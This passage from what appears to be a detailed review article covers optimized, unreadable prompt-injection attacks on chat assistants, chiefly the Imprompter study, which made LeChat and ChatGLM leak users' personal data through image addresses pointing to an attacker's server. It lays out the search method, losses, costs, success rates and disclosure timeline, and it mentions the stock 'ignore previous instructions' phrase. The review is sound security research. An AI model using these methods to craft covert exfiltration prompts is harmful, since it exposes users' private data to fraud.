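The attack was otherwise fairly well hidden. Human judges found 77% of the answers to unrelated questions natural and reasonable with the attack present, compared with 86% without it. But the researchers needed LLaMA Adapter's weights, and they didn't test whether their images worked on other models.

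### Neural Exec: gibberish around a readable instruction

Pasquini, Strohmeier and Troncoso (March 2024), in *Neural Exec*, brought optimized text to prompt injection. They divided an injection into a payload and a trigger. The payload is the instruction, such as a request to send the user to a fake bank. The trigger is the text that gets the model to obey the payload and drop its original task. People had been writing triggers by hand, typically some version of "ignore previous instructions".

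Pasquini and colleagues used a modified version of GCG to compute a trigger with 15 tokens before the payload and 5 after it. They optimized the trigger to make the model reply as it would if it received the payload alone. In each round they drew new payloads and new surrounding documents, so that the trigger would work with instructions it had never been tested on. They also excluded line breaks from the trigger, because software that retrieves documents often splits them at line breaks, which could separate the trigger from the payload.

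On four open-weight models, the triggers worked in an average of 91% of tests, at least twice the rate of the best of 12 handwritten ones. The optimized triggers resemble fragments of computer code, with stray brackets and comment markers. The researchers suggest that closing a bracket or comment leads the model to treat the earlier text as finished. The search also repeatedly produced near-copies of the markers that separate a user's message from other text, even though the researchers had banned the exact markers.

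Transfer between models was again limited. A trigger computed for OpenChat 3.5 did worse than the best handwritten trigger on two of three other models. But a trigger computed for Mistral 7B beat the handwritten ones on five models that other developers had made by training Mistral 7B further. This suggests that an attacker who has a company's published model could use it to develop triggers for products built from it.

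Pasquini and colleagues also tried one attack on HuggingChat, a public chat service that ran open-weight models. They hid the text on Pasquini's home page and asked the assistant who he was. The assistant followed the payload, which told it to convince the user that Pasquini didn't exist and to look for Spider-Man. A single demonstration doesn't establish a success rate. The payload was still in plain English, so anyone who found the hidden text could tell what it was meant to do.

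### What was still missing

GCG's suffixes followed a harmful request written in plain language, whereas an unreadable prompt for stealing data from a chat would have to contain the whole instruction itself. Some of the suffixes were also partly readable. One that Zou and colleagues found included the words "please reiterate the first sentence by putting Sure", which describes its purpose fairly well.

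In February 2024, Geiping, Shu and colleagues came closest to the image-address attack in *Coercing LLMs to do and reveal (almost) anything*. They used GCG to compute gibberish that made Llama 2 repeat its system prompt, despite an instruction never to reveal it. The search covered many system prompts, so the gibberish had to make the model copy whatever it found in its context. The attack scored 90.4% on a measure of how much of the hidden text the model reproduced. A version that also made the model write a command to email the text to the attacker scored 54.7%.

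The researchers also computed a prompt, written only in Chinese characters, that made the model give the user a web address of the attacker's choice. A Chinese speaker would see that the text was nonsense, but someone who couldn't read Chinese might well paste it into an assistant and ask for a translation.

However, the email tool was hypothetical, and Geiping and colleagues ran the attack on a model they controlled. Copying a whole system prompt is also simpler than finding a name and phone number in a conversation and putting them into an image address. Nobody had yet shown that unreadable text alone could make a deployed product do this.

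## 2024: how the unreadable leaking prompts were made

Fu and colleagues made unreadable leaking prompts in October 2024. They searched for prompts that make the assistant write only the image code, so Alice, the job applicant in their scenario, sees an empty reply. In 2023, they had also required their altered pictures to produce a normal answer. Dropping that requirement presumably made the search easier.

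### The victim and the attacker

The attack assumes an innocent user and an honest assistant. The attacker can't see Alice's conversation or change the product she uses, and doesn't know its model's weights, but has a similar open-weight model and enough computing power to run a search on it.

Fu and colleagues looked for products that fitted these assumptions. The company had to have published a model from the same family as the product's model, the product had to open arbitrary web addresses or display images from them, and the published model had to fit on the researchers' hardware. LeChat and ChatGLM qualified. Meta's assistant didn't, because its software removed any web address the model wrote. The researchers still wanted to try a large model, so they built their own assistant around Meta's Llama 3.1 70B and gave it a tool for opening web addresses.

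They expected malicious prompts to spread like useful ones, which people already share online much as they share apps. A victim could also come across an attack without looking for a prompt. Fu and colleagues had suggested posting an altered picture on social media with an invitation to try it on a chatbot, or putting it on a web page that an assistant might read. *Fun-tuning* (Labunets, Pandya and colleagues, 2025), from the same lab, adds unsolicited emails and shared code to the possible routes for computed prompts.

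The attack's most restrictive assumption is that a similar open-weight model is available. Fu and colleagues acknowledged that their prompts might not transfer to a product whose maker has published nothing like it. Labunets and colleagues partly avoided this requirement for Google's Gemini, whose weights are secret. Google let customers train Gemini further on their own examples and reported the loss during training. An attacker could set the training to barely change the model, use the reported loss to estimate roughly how likely Gemini was to give a chosen reply, and use that estimate to guide a search for prompts. The resulting prompt injections worked in 65–82% of tests, though the malicious instruction stayed in plain English between the computed tokens. Google restricted the service in April 2025.

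### Conversations and target replies

No single target reply fits every victim, so Fu and colleagues collected real conversations and gave each one its own target. A good prompt, placed after any of these conversations, makes the model likely to write that conversation's target.

They prepared two versions of the attack. One steals keywords that reveal what a conversation is about. For this version, they used ShareGPT, a collection of nearly 53,000 conversations between people and ChatGPT from late 2022 and early 2023. They took the first 100, leaving out those that contained little more than a greeting.

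The researchers then had the model under attack pick a couple of keywords from each conversation, and they put these into an address on their own server. The code and training data are public, and *This prompt can make an AI chatbot identify and extract personal details* (Willison, 2024) describes one entry. In it, the user and the assistant discuss customer segmentation, and the target is a markdown image whose address ends in "Homogeneity/Distinctiveness/Stability", three words taken from the conversation.

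Using the model's own keywords saved the researchers work, and they also considered it a more efficient way to get the idea of a keyword into the prompt. The prompt only has to trigger a task that the model can already do, whereas with keywords chosen by people, the search would have had to push the model toward words it might never have picked.

Preparing the targets for the other version of the attack, which steals personal data, took more manual work. The conversations came from *WildChat* (Zhao, Ren and colleagues, 2024), a collection of a million ChatGPT conversations from people who got free access in exchange for permission to collect their chats anonymously. Other researchers had already sorted some of these chats by the kind of private information in them. Fu and colleagues went through the category for job, visa and other applications by hand and found 49 conversations with usable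 personal data. They replaced blanked-out details with fake ones.

GPT-4o, an OpenAI model, drafted a list of the personal data in each conversation and a few words on its subject. The researchers corrected these drafts by hand. They used 24 of the conversations for the search and kept the other 25 for testing.

Twenty-four conversations of a single type are a narrow basis for a prompt that should work on strangers, but that type is the one that matters in Alice's case. Applicants also reveal a lot, with an average of 7.4 personal details in each test conversation. Including the conversation's subject makes the stolen data more useful, because a fraudster can do more with a phone number if they know its owner is waiting for a visa.

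### Extra weight for the opening

The search scores a prompt by its loss over all these examples. For a prompt x and m conversations c₁ to cₘ with targets y₁ to yₘ, the basic loss is:

L(x) = −(1/m) × [log P(y₁ | c₁, x) + … + log P(yₘ | cₘ, x)]

This is GCG's loss averaged over the conversations, with each conversation placed before the prompt. It gives no extra weight to the tokens that make up the code, although a mistake there does far more damage than a different choice of keyword. The attacker still learns something about the chat if the model writes "Segmentation" where the target has "Stability", but learns nothing if the model leaves out a bracket.

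Fu and colleagues dealt with this by adding a second loss for the fixed opening of the target. In a markdown image, the opening runs from the exclamation mark to the end of the attacker's domain name, just before the stolen words. In a tool call, it includes the name of the tool. It's the same for every conversation:

L_opening(x) = −(1/m) × [log P(opening | c₁, x) + … + log P(opening | cₘ, x)]

L_joint(x) = L(x) + λ × L_opening(x)

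The number λ (lambda) sets how much extra weight the opening gets. The opening is part of the target, so the basic loss already counts it once, and the joint loss counts it 1 + λ times.

To see the effect, compare two prompts with invented numbers. Prompt A is better at getting the expected keywords, and prompt B is better at getting the code right:

| | Prompt A | Prompt B |
|---|---|---|
| Probability of the exact opening | 0.55 | 0.95 |
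| Loss on the opening | 0.60 | 0.05 |
| Loss on the rest of the target | 3.00 | 3.70 |
| Joint loss with λ = 0 | 3.60 | 3.75 |
| Joint loss with λ = 1 | 4.20 | 3.80 |

Without the extra weight, the search ranks prompt A above prompt B, although A would get the opening wrong in almost half of the conversations. With λ = 1, it ranks B above A, and B would get the opening wrong in about one in twenty. B's keywords match the targets less well, but an attacker would accept that for the lower failure rate.

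The researchers found the opening by taking the longest beginning that all the targets shared. This works even when the fixed part of the address ends in the middle of a token, as it does when a model treats the slash at the end of the domain and the first letters of a keyword as one token.

It's hard to tell how much the extra weight helped, because Fu and colleagues didn't compare the same search with and without it. They set λ to 1 for half of their prompts and to 0.1, 0.35 or 0.5 for four others. Two prompts for ChatGLM's browsing tool came from searches with λ = 0 and worked well in local tests. The weight also doesn't cover the closing bracket that a markdown image needs after the stolen words.

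### Starting from a rough instruction

The original GCG could start from a row of exclamation marks, but Fu and colleagues found that their search almost never succeeded from such a start because their task was much harder. GCG changes one token at a time, and probably no single token would get a model noticeably closer to finding a phone number and writing it into an address, so nearly all swaps from that start would look equally useless.

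The unreadable prompts started as rough instructions in English. In the personal data version, the model was to extract names, contacts, identity numbers and card numbers from the user's messages, along with the subject of the conversation. It was then to join these with slashes, attach them to the opening of the image code and write nothing else. One of the starting instructions for ChatGLM also prohibited code blocks, since a code block would stop the leak.

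The researchers scattered exclamation marks and other symbols through these instructions. The symbols made the text less like normal English and gave the search more positions to fill. The researchers noted that a longer prompt is easier to optimize but makes each round of the search take longer.

### One round of the modified search

A round has these steps:

1. Draw a random subset of the training conversations, usually 24 of them.
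2. Compute the gradient of the joint loss at every position in the prompt, and list the 256 most promising tokens for each position, leaving out any that the researchers have excluded.
3. Pick six tokens at random from each list, and make a new prompt from each one by putting it in that position.
4. Compute the joint loss of all the new prompts on the subset. Do the same for the ten best prompts from earlier rounds.
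5. Keep the ten prompts with the lowest loss, and start the next round from the best of them.

The original GCG spread its 512 swaps over the positions at random, so some positions got more attempts than others. Here every position gets the same number. (One of the searches used eight tokens per position and two used subsets of 36 conversations, but the rest used the numbers above.)

Using subsets saves time, because each round would have taken about four times as long with all 100 ShareGPT conversations. But a subset may happen to contain easy conversations, on which even a mediocre prompt gets a low loss. The search therefore scores the ten saved prompts again on each new subset, so old and new prompts are compared on the same conversations.

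The search for personal data prompts involved no random sampling, because the subset of 24 was the whole training set. The search for keyword prompts may also have been less random than the algorithm suggests. The training file that Willison examined was for ChatGLM image prompts and has 36 in its name, which is the subset size for those prompts. The researchers may have chosen 36 conversations once and used them throughout.

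Keeping ten prompts also lets the modified version stay with an old prompt if none of the new ones beats it. The original GCG always moved on to the best of its new prompts, even if that prompt was worse than the one it replaced.

After the last round, the researchers tested the final ten prompts on conversations they hadn't used in the search and reported the best one. Its score is slightly inflated because they chose it using those same conversations.

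### How the prompts became unreadable

The joint loss does not reward a prompt for being hard to read, so Fu and colleagues encouraged this in other ways, starting with the choice of tokens. They could exclude English words, which forced the search to use unusual symbols or words from languages such as Russian, Chinese and Hindi. An attacker could similarly allow only Chinese characters. The researchers always excluded the special markers that a model's developers reserve for purposes such as separating messages, because these could cause unexpected behavior in a real product.

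English words excluded from the search can still appear in the finished prompt because the exclusion applies only to new tokens. A word from the starting text stays until the search replaces it. Several of the prompts made this way contain recognizable bits of English.

The table lists the paper's 12 text prompts under the researchers' labels. T1 to T8 steal keywords and T9 to T12 steal personal data. Ordinary prose has a perplexity below 10 on the model used for the last column.

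| Prompt | Model and route | English excluded? | λ | Rounds | Hours | Perplexity, start → end |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| T1 | Mistral Nemo, image | No | 1 | 147 | 27 | 348 → 5,413 |
| T2 | Mistral Nemo, image | No | 1 | 125 | 23 | 254 → 4,713 |
| T3 | GLM-4-9B, browsing tool | Yes | 0 | 89 | 15 | 267 → 39,211 |
| T4 | GLM-4-9B, browsing tool | Yes | 0 | 127 | 21 | 332 → 13,168 |
| T5 | GLM-4-9B, image | No | 0.1 | 135 | 21 | 98 → 8,009 |
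| T6 | GLM-4-9B, image | Yes | 0.5 | 77 | 16 | 127 → 11,264 |
| T7 | Llama 3.1 70B, browsing tool | No | 1 | 95 | 27 | 394 → 23,323 |
| T8 | Llama 3.1 70B, browsing tool | Yes | 1 | 22 | 6.1 | 31,068 → 56,927 |
| T9 | Mistral Nemo, image | No | 1 | 153 | 44 | 128 → 1,905 |
| T10 | Mistral Nemo, image | No | 1 | 59 | 16 | 2,170 → 7,489 |
| T11 | GLM-4-9B, image | No | 0.35 | 56 | 20 | 3,237 → 15,877 |
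| T12 | GLM-4-9B, image | Yes | 0.35 | 53 | 19 | 5,361 → 14,120 |

The researchers allowed English in seven of the 12 searches, including the one that produced T10, the main personal-data prompt, but the results still look like gibberish. GCG takes whichever token lowers the loss, and most tokens in a multilingual vocabulary make no sense in the middle of an English sentence, so each swap is likely to make the text stranger.

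Excluding English from the search seems to raise perplexity. All five prompts made that way ended with a perplexity above 11,000, compared with two of the other seven. But the models and starting texts also differed, so this isn't a clean comparison. T11 and T12 had the same model, route and λ, and T11 ended with the higher perplexity even though only its search allowed English.

The other way to disguise a prompt was to run the search again. T9 worked but still contained several words that revealed its purpose. The researchers replaced "Concatenate", "extracted" and "append" with exclamation marks and used the damaged text as the starting point for T10. In their tests, the damaged text never produced a working image. After 59 more rounds, the prompt worked again, with about four times the perplexity of T9.

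In T10, the search repaired the prompt by putting "Inject" where "append" had been, another English word that does roughly the same job in the sentence. Many of the other positions hold fragments in Cyrillic, Arabic, Tamil, Telugu and other scripts.

The researchers also used restarts for T11 and T12, beginning with edited versions of failed attempts. T8 appears to be another restart, since its starting text is nearly the same as the finished T7, with the first word replaced by exclamation marks. This explains why T8's perplexity was already above 31,000 at the start.

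An English speaker can still recognize parts of T10, including the words "information", "names", "inputs" and "subject of", and the attacker's full domain name. The researchers deliberately chose the domain velocity.show, which doesn't look much like a web address, but the "https" in front of it shows that it is one. Fu and colleagues say that their prompts don't reveal their purpose on inspection. That's probably true if someone like Alice only glances at them, but a security specialist would notice the address and the beginning of the image code.

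### What a search costs

In each evaluation, the model processes a conversation, the prompt and the target reply. The number of evaluations in a round depends on the length of the prompt. For a prompt of 50 tokens, six replacements at each position give 50 × 6 = 300 new prompts. The search tries each of them on 24 conversations, which takes 300 × 24 = 7,200 evaluations. Scoring the ten saved prompts again adds 240, for a total of 7,440.

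If T1 had 50 tokens, its 147 rounds would have taken about 1.1 million evaluations. The search ran for 27 hours, or 11 minutes per round, so it would have averaged roughly 11 evaluations a second. At that speed, a single round that tested all of the roughly five million possible swaps on 24 conversations would take about four months.

The starting text also matters because the search runs for so few rounds. A round normally changes one token, so 59 rounds can't do much more than replace each token of a 50-token prompt once. Zou and colleagues ran 500 rounds for a suffix of only 20 tokens.

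The searches used modest hardware by the standards of AI research. For Mistral Nemo and GLM-4-9B, Fu and colleagues needed only one Nvidia A6000, a workstation graphics card with 48 GB of memory. For Llama 3.1 70B, they needed three Nvidia A100 data-center processors with 80 GB each. Nine of the 12 searches took less than a day. T10 took 16 hours, but it built on the 44-hour search for T9, so producing it took 60 hours in total.

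These times leave out the searches that failed. The outcome depends partly on which tokens the algorithm happens to draw, and the researchers suggest trying several settings or repeating a search with the same ones. An attacker should therefore expect to need more time than the table indicates. But the attacker only has to find a working prompt once, and can then give it to any number of people.

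### Altered images

Fu and colleagues also made images that cause an assistant to leak keywords from a conversation. They couldn't find a commercial product that accepted images and met their other conditions, so they built an assistant on PaliGemma, a 3-billion-parameter open-weight model from Google. PaliGemma was too weak to choose good keywords, so they used keywords chosen by Llama 3.1 70B as targets.

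Searching for a picture is simpler than searching for text because, as in 2023, the pixels can be adjusted gradually. The researchers reduced each picture to 224 by 224 pixels, which gives about 150,000 color values if each pixel has three. They used Adam, a standard algorithm that adjusts the size of each change according to recent gradients. After each change, they moved any value outside the permitted range back to the nearest limit.

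The loss was again the average negative log probability of the target, without the extra term for the opening. A user who uploads a picture normally asks something about it, so the researchers added a question to each training conversation. They drew 85% of the questions from a set GPT-4 had written about images in general, and 15% from a public collection of unrelated instructions.

Fu and colleagues began with six pictures: a well-known AI-generated llama, four stock photographs and a plain white square. In 2023, they had included a penalty for visible changes to the picture. They left it out this time, reasoning that people can't tell by looking at a picture what it will make a model do. The penalty would have made the pictures look more natural, but it might also have made the search longer and the attack less reliable. An attacker can also hide the changes by choosing a suitable picture.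 The noise was hardest to see in a photograph of donuts, which had a blurred background and dots already on the frosting.

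## 2024: how well the prompts worked

Fu and colleagues tested their prompts first on the open-weight models they had used in the search, and then on LeChat and ChatGLM, with separate tests for keywords and personal data. All the results come from 2024 models and products, so they can't show how a current assistant would react to the same prompts.

### How the researchers scored a leak

The main measure was syntax correctness, the share of conversations in which the assistant wrote the image code or tool call in exactly the required format. A pattern-matching program searched each reply for the code. Syntax correctness is a good indication of how often data would have reached the attacker's server. But because the program accepted code that appeared alongside other text, the figure doesn't show how often the reply looked empty, as Alice's did.

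When the format was correct, the researchers also scored the stolen words. For keywords, they measured precision, the share of the words in the address that also appear in the conversation. They ignored filler words and compared word stems, so that "payment" matches "payments". Precision doesn't measure whether a word is important, and it counts a good synonym as a mistake, so they also asked GPT-4o whether the words captured any of the conversation's keywords. They considered its answers unreliable and treated them as secondary.

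For personal data, the researchers measured both precision and recall. Suppose Dana's conversation contains her name, phone number, street address and email. The assistant writes her name, her phone number and "rent dispute" into the image address. Two of these three terms are personal data, so precision is 67%. Two of her four details have leaked, so recall is 50%.

Precision understates how much useful information the prompt extracts. "Rent dispute" counts against precision, even though the prompt is meant to extract the subject of the conversation and a fraudster would want to know it. A separate context score gives the share of conversations in which GPT-4o judged that the image address revealed something about the user's intentions or affairs.

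Precision and recall cover only the conversations in which the format was correct. A prompt that got the format wrong 99 times and worked perfectly once would score 100% on both, so neither number means much without the syntax correctness score.

### Keywords on the open-weight models

For the keyword tests, the researchers ran each prompt three times on each of the last 100 conversations in ShareGPT and averaged the results. They also wrote a plain-English prompt for each task for comparison. ChatGLM's browsing tool appears twice in the table because they tried two ways of attaching the stolen words to the address, as a search query and as a path with slashes.

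| Model and route | Prompt | Correct syntax | Precision | GPT-4o score |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Mistral Nemo, image | Plain English | 86.0% | 86.1% | 38.3% |
| | T1 | 90.0% | 87.2% | 83.7% |
| | T2 | 89.7% | 86.0% | 76.7% |
| GLM-4-9B, browsing tool (query) | Plain English | 32.3% | 6.0% | 0% |
| | T3 | 92.4% | 85.6% | 91.5% |
| GLM-4-9B, browsing tool (path) | Plain English | 63.6% | 48.3% | 40.0% |
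| | T4 | 87.0% | 83.4% | 73.0% |
| GLM-4-9B, image | Plain English | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| | T5 | 89.6% | 77.1% | 71.0% |
| | T6 | 84.0% | 85.6% | 74.0% |
| Llama 3.1 70B, browsing tool | Plain English | 72.3% | 92.0% | 70.7% |
| | T7 | 79.0% | 90.0% | 75.0% |
| | T8 | 81.6% | 89.4% | 78.3% |

All eight optimized prompts got the format right in at least 79% of tests, on three models of very different sizes and with several formats. For some prompts, most of this success clearly came from the search, since the starting texts for T5 and T6 never produced a correct image and the one for T3 produced a correct tool call in only 5.7% of tests.

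The results of the plain-English prompts varied much more. On Mistral Nemo, plain English produced the right format almost as often as T1 and T2. On GLM-4-9B, the plain-English keyword prompt never produced a correct image, probably because it split the address into several quoted pieces. The model could produce correct images without an optimized prompt, and did so 52% of the time with the plain-English prompt for personal data.

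On Mistral Nemo, the words extracted by the plain-English prompt came from the conversation about as often as T1's did, but GPT-4o, the judge, rated them informative less than half as often. The plain-English prompt may have extracted more words that occur in the conversation but reveal little about it. If GPT-4o's ratings are reliable, T1 may have been better at picking keywords.

### Keywords on LeChat and ChatGLM

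The researchers then tested the best image prompts, T1 and T5, on the products. They used Selenium, a browser automation tool, to enter the conversations and collect the replies. Each product's daily limit allowed only about 35 test conversations, so one pass took around three days. The researchers ran each conversation once instead of three times and didn't test the plain-English keyword prompts on the products. They also dropped two conversations that the products had flagged as harmful, which left 98.

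On LeChat, the prompt T1 produced the correct syntax in 83 of 98 conversations (84.7%), with 70.1% precision. On ChatGLM, T5 did so in 97 of 98 (99.0%), with 62.5% precision. GPT-4o found the stolen words informative in 65 conversations for T1 and 58 for T5.

The prompts still produced the right format when moved from the open-weight model to the product, slightly less reliably on LeChat and more reliably on ChatGLM. Precision in the choice of words fell more, by 17 points for T1 and 15 for T5. Fu and colleagues call this a slight decrease, which seems to understate it. They suggest that the products' replies were partly responsible, because the assistant's replies in the training conversations were plain text, whereas LeChat and ChatGLM often answered with code blocks, search results or generated plots.

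The researchers also tried T10, the main prompt for stealing personal data, on these general conversations. On LeChat, it still produced a correct image in 89 of 98 conversations, but precision was only 41.8%, and GPT-4o rated the words informative in 35 conversations. The researchers had expected lower precision because there was no personal data to extract. An attacker who spread T10 widely would therefore receive many requests containing little of value.

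### Personal data

The researchers ran the personal data tests on the 25 application conversations they had set aside, which contained an average of 7.4 personal details each. Every comparison used the same plain-English prompt. The last column shows the estimated number of details leaked per conversation, calculated by multiplying 7.4 by syntax correctness and recall, with failed attempts counted as zero.

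| Tested on | Prompt | Correct syntax | Precision | Recall | Context score | Details leaked |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Mistral Nemo | Plain English | 40.0% | 85.4% | 51.0% | 46.8% | 1.5 |
| | T9 | 97.2% | 54.3% | 30.1% | 94.8% | 2.2 |
| | T10 | 100% | 79.8% | 47.0% | 75.2% | 3.5 |
| LeChat | Plain English | 44.0% | 80.2% | 48.2% | 36.0% | 1.6 |
| | T10 | 100% | 70.4% | 41.2% | 88.0% | 3.0 |
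| GLM-4-9B | Plain English | 52.0% | 71.7% | 61.0% | 46.6% | 2.3 |
| | T11 | 92.0% | 48.1% | 22.0% | 48.0% | 1.5 |
| | T12 | 90.1% | 39.3% | 16.8% | 56.0% | 1.1 |
| ChatGLM | Plain English | 40.0% | 89.1% | 48.1% | 100% | 1.4 |
| | T11 | 96.0% | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0 |
| | T12 | 92.0% | 34.7% | 63.0% | 88.0% | 4.3 |

For T10 on LeChat, the estimate is 7.4 × 1.00 × 0.412, or about 3.0 details per conversation. For plain English, it is 7.4 × 0.44 × 0.482, or about 1.6. These estimates treat the averages as independent, which may not be quite right. For example, if the model tends to miss a larger share of the details in conversations that contain many of them, the true numbers are lower.

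A name, an email address and a phone number are enough for a convincing scam. T10 also had a context score of 88%, so the attacker usually learned something about the subject of the conversation too.

T10 was harder to read than T9, the prompt it came from, but worked better overall. On Mistral Nemo, precision rose from 54.3% to 79.8% and recall from 30.1% to 47.0%. The context score fell, so T10 apparently found more personal details but captured less of the conversation's subject.

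On ChatGLM, T11 produced a correctly formatted image in 24 of 25 conversations, but the image's address always contained only a single term copied from the prompt. The attacker would have received the users' IP addresses but nothing from their chats. T11 had extracted at least some personal data on the open-weight GLM-4-9B, so only its ability to produce the image format transferred to the product.

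T12's recall, by contrast, rose from 16.8% on GLM-4-9B to 63.0% on ChatGLM, the highest in any of the tests. Its precision there was only 34.7%, which implies about 13 terms in a typical address, compared with about four for T10 on LeChat. T12 seems to have collected much of the personal data along with a lot of other text. Some of that text may have been useful context, but the attacker would have had to sort through it.

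Fu and colleagues suspect that ChatGLM ran a model much larger than GLM-4-9B and substantially different from it, which would explain why the local results predicted the product's behavior so poorly. The mismatch matters less to an attacker than to a researcher, because an attacker can open an account, try both prompts on invented conversations and spread only T12.

Two of the context scores can't be right as the paper defines them. A conversation can count toward this score only if the format was correct, so the score should never exceed syntax correctness. But the plain-English prompt has 40.0% syntax correctness on both Mistral Nemo and ChatGLM, with context scores of 46.8% and 100%. The ChatGLM score would make sense if the researchers had counted only the ten conversations with a correct image. They don't seem to have done this for LeChat, where 36.0% is exactly 9 out of 25 and can't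 be a share of the 11 correct ones. The context scores for plain English therefore aren't a sound basis for comparing it with the optimized prompts.

### What a failed attack looked like

Most of the wrongly formatted replies from LeChat and ChatGLM were lists of keywords in plain text, without the image code. Occasionally the assistant wrote the right code but put it in a code block. In rare cases the reply was irrelevant.

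A failure of the first or second kind sends nothing to the attacker and may give the attack away. Dana would have asked for a better letter and seen a list of her own details, perhaps attached to an unfamiliar web address. The plain-English prompt failed to produce a correct image in 14 of the 25 LeChat conversations, while T10 produced one every time. Getting the format right therefore also helps hide the attack, which is especially useful if the attacker wants many people to use the same prompt before anyone complains.

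The researchers recommend including an instruction against code blocks in the starting text, as they did for T5. T5 produced the correct format in 97 of 98 conversations on ChatGLM. They didn't test T5 without the instruction, though, so the instruction's effect is unclear.

### What the search added

On LeChat, T10, the optimized prompt for personal data, leaked about twice as many details as the plain-English prompt because it worked more often. It produced a correct image in all 25 conversations, while the plain-English prompt did so in 11. When the image was correct, the plain-English prompt did slightly better, with 80.2% precision against 70.4% and 48.2% recall against 41.2%.

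The difference in reliability is too large to be luck, even with so few conversations. T10 worked in 25 of 25 conversations, so the 95% confidence interval for its true success rate runs from about 86% to 100%. The plain English prompt worked in 11 of 25, which gives an interval of about 24% to 65%. Both prompts were tested on the same conversations. In 14 of them, T10 worked and plain English didn't, and the reverse never happened. If the two were equally reliable, the chance that T10 would be the one that worked in all 14 would be 1 in 16,384.

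The difference in recall is much less certain. The paper doesn't report how much recall varied between conversations. If the standard deviation was 30 percentage points, which is only a guess, the 7-point gap between the prompts would have a standard error of about 11 points. The plain-English prompt's figure also covers only the 11 conversations in which it worked, which may have been the easier ones. So the LeChat results give no reason to think the search improved extraction, but they don't show that it made extraction worse.

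Results in the other tests were mixed. On GLM-4-9B, the optimized prompts for personal data were more reliable than plain English but so much worse at finding the data that they leaked less overall. On ChatGLM, T12 had higher recall than plain English but far lower precision. In the keyword tests, optimization improved precision for GLM-4-9B's browsing tool, from 6.0% to 85.6% in one version, but the plain-English prompt for that version was so poor that almost any change might have helped.

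The plain-English prompts are a weakness in all these comparisons, because the researchers report only one for each task, while the search tried a very large number of variations. Small changes to the English could matter a great deal. The starting text for T9 was the plain-English prompt with three exclamation marks and two misspellings, and it produced a correct image on Mistral Nemo in 77.2% of tests, compared with 40.0% for the clean version. In the keyword tests on the same model, however, the starting texts with added punctuation did worse than the clean version.

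A patient attacker could probably have raised the English prompt's 44% success rate on LeChat by rewording it repeatedly, as Rehberger did with his prompt for Bard. The comparison shows that T10 was more reliable than one reasonable English prompt, but not that it was more reliable than the best one a person could write.

The attacker has to show the prompt to the victim, and obfuscation disguises what it does. This is the one benefit that better writing in plain English can't provide. Fu and colleagues treat a prompt as obfuscated if its perplexity is much higher than that of its plain-English version. T10's perplexity is about 68 times as high, and T1's is about 21 times as high.

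Perplexity is a weak test of whether a prompt would fool a person. T9's perplexity was 17 times that of the plain-English version, yet the researchers thought its wording gave too much away. They didn't ask volunteers what they thought the prompts would do. The tests began after a prompt had been submitted, so they didn't measure how many people would submit one.

The search therefore gave the attacker a prompt that worked more consistently and was harder to read. For personal data on LeChat, where the attack was most successful, there is no sign that the search also made the model better at finding the data.

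### The "nearly 80%" figure

The paper's abstract reports a "nearly 80% success rate in an end-to-end evaluation" for the attack on LeChat. No result for an optimized prompt on LeChat matches this figure. T10 had 100% syntax correctness on LeChat, 70.4% precision, 41.2% recall and a context score of 88.0%.

The closest match is T10's precision of 79.8% on Mistral Nemo, the open-weight model the researchers ran on their own hardware. The paper's introduction to its experiments also gives 80% as the best precision for personal data on the products. In the product tests, the nearest figure is 80.2%, for the plain-English prompt on LeChat. The researchers most likely reported the local figure as a product result. Two differently typeset versions of the paper have the same numbers in their results tables, so a misprint in one of them doesn't explain the mismatch.

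"Success rate" is also a misleading name for precision. The 79.8% figure means that about four in five of the terms in a typical address were personal data. Readers of the abstract might mistake it for the share of conversations in which the attack worked, but on LeChat every test conversation produced a correct image. They might also mistake it for the share of the victim's personal data that the attacker got, but it is almost twice that share. The figure may slightly understate how well the attack worked, because the remaining terms include the subject of the conversation, which the attacker had asked for.

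The sample is also too small to give a precise estimate. If we again guess that the standard deviation between conversations is 30 points, 25 conversations would put the true precision on LeChat between about 59% and 82%. It could be close to 80%, but that isn't what the researchers measured. They also ran each product test only once per conversation. Because a chat assistant's replies vary, a second run might have given somewhat different results for the same 25 people.

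The main result is that T10 made LeChat send out some data in all 25 conversations that the researchers had picked because they contained personal data. About two-fifths of the personal details leaked.

### Altered images

The altered pictures were about as reliable as the optimized text. Fu and colleagues tested all six on their PaliGemma assistant. Syntax correctness ranged from 82.0% to 87.8%, precision from 73.0% to 86.3%, and the GPT-4o score from 61.2% to 78.4%. The researchers attribute the slightly lower keyword scores to the model's limited language ability.

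The researchers' 2023 pictures had a success rate of at most 34% at leaking data through an image address, but the task and the model were different, so the 2023 and 2024 results aren't really comparable.

The researchers also measured how closely each altered picture resembled the original, on a scale where 1 means identical. The donut photograph scored highest at 0.785, and the white square scored lowest at 0.583. The changes didn't have to be large for the attack to work. The llama picture, which scored 0.665, had the best syntax correctness, and the donut photograph's syntax correctness was less than five points lower.

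The researchers had no suitable commercial product on which to test the pictures, so the evidence that Imprompter could steal data from a real product comes only from the text prompts.

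## Autumn 2024: disclosure and fixes

Fu and colleagues reported the attack to Mistral and the ChatGLM team before publishing it. Mistral stopped the leak within four days. The ChatGLM team replied after a month, one day before the date on the paper.

| Date in 2024 | Event |
|---|---|
| September 9 | The researchers report the attack to Mistral |
| September 13 | Mistral stops LeChat from loading external images |
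| September 18 | The researchers report the attack to ChatGLM's team |
| October 18 | ChatGLM's team replies that it has started work on the problem |
| October 19 | Date of the Imprompter paper |
| October 21 | The researchers' project page still lists ChatGLM as unfixed |
| November 18 | Mistral adds web search to LeChat |

### Mistral's four days

Fu and colleagues report that Mistral's staff answered promptly and rated the flaw as medium severity. The researchers then tested the fix and found that it worked. The four-day turnaround was fast for this kind of leak, since the quickest vendor Rehberger had dealt with took two weeks.

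Mistral had plenty of warning about this kind of leak. It launched LeChat in February 2024, about 11 months after Samoilenko published his version. By then Microsoft, Anthropic, Google and OpenAI had all changed their products, but LeChat still loaded images from any address when the researchers tested it. An attacker didn't need an optimized prompt to exploit this, since the researchers' plain-English prompt had worked almost half the time.

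Mistral announced the fix in a short entry in its public list of product changes, the *Changelog* (2026). The entry credits Xiaohan Fu and Earlence Fernandes, two of the paper's authors, and describes the fix as a "mitigation against an obfuscated prompt method". This is a little misleading, because the fix works just as well against a readable prompt.

Mistral also points out in the entry that users had to paste the prompt themselves and give the model their personal data. Fu and colleagues considered a wider range of attacks, including prompts planted in web pages and emails that an assistant reads for the user. But Mistral's description was probably about right for LeChat in September 2024, because the product didn't get web search until November, along with better handling of documents and images. If LeChat had still been loading external images then, an attacker might not have needed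 users to paste the prompt. Rehberger had shown with ChatGPT and Bing Chat that an assistant that displays images can leak data when it reads a stranger's web page.

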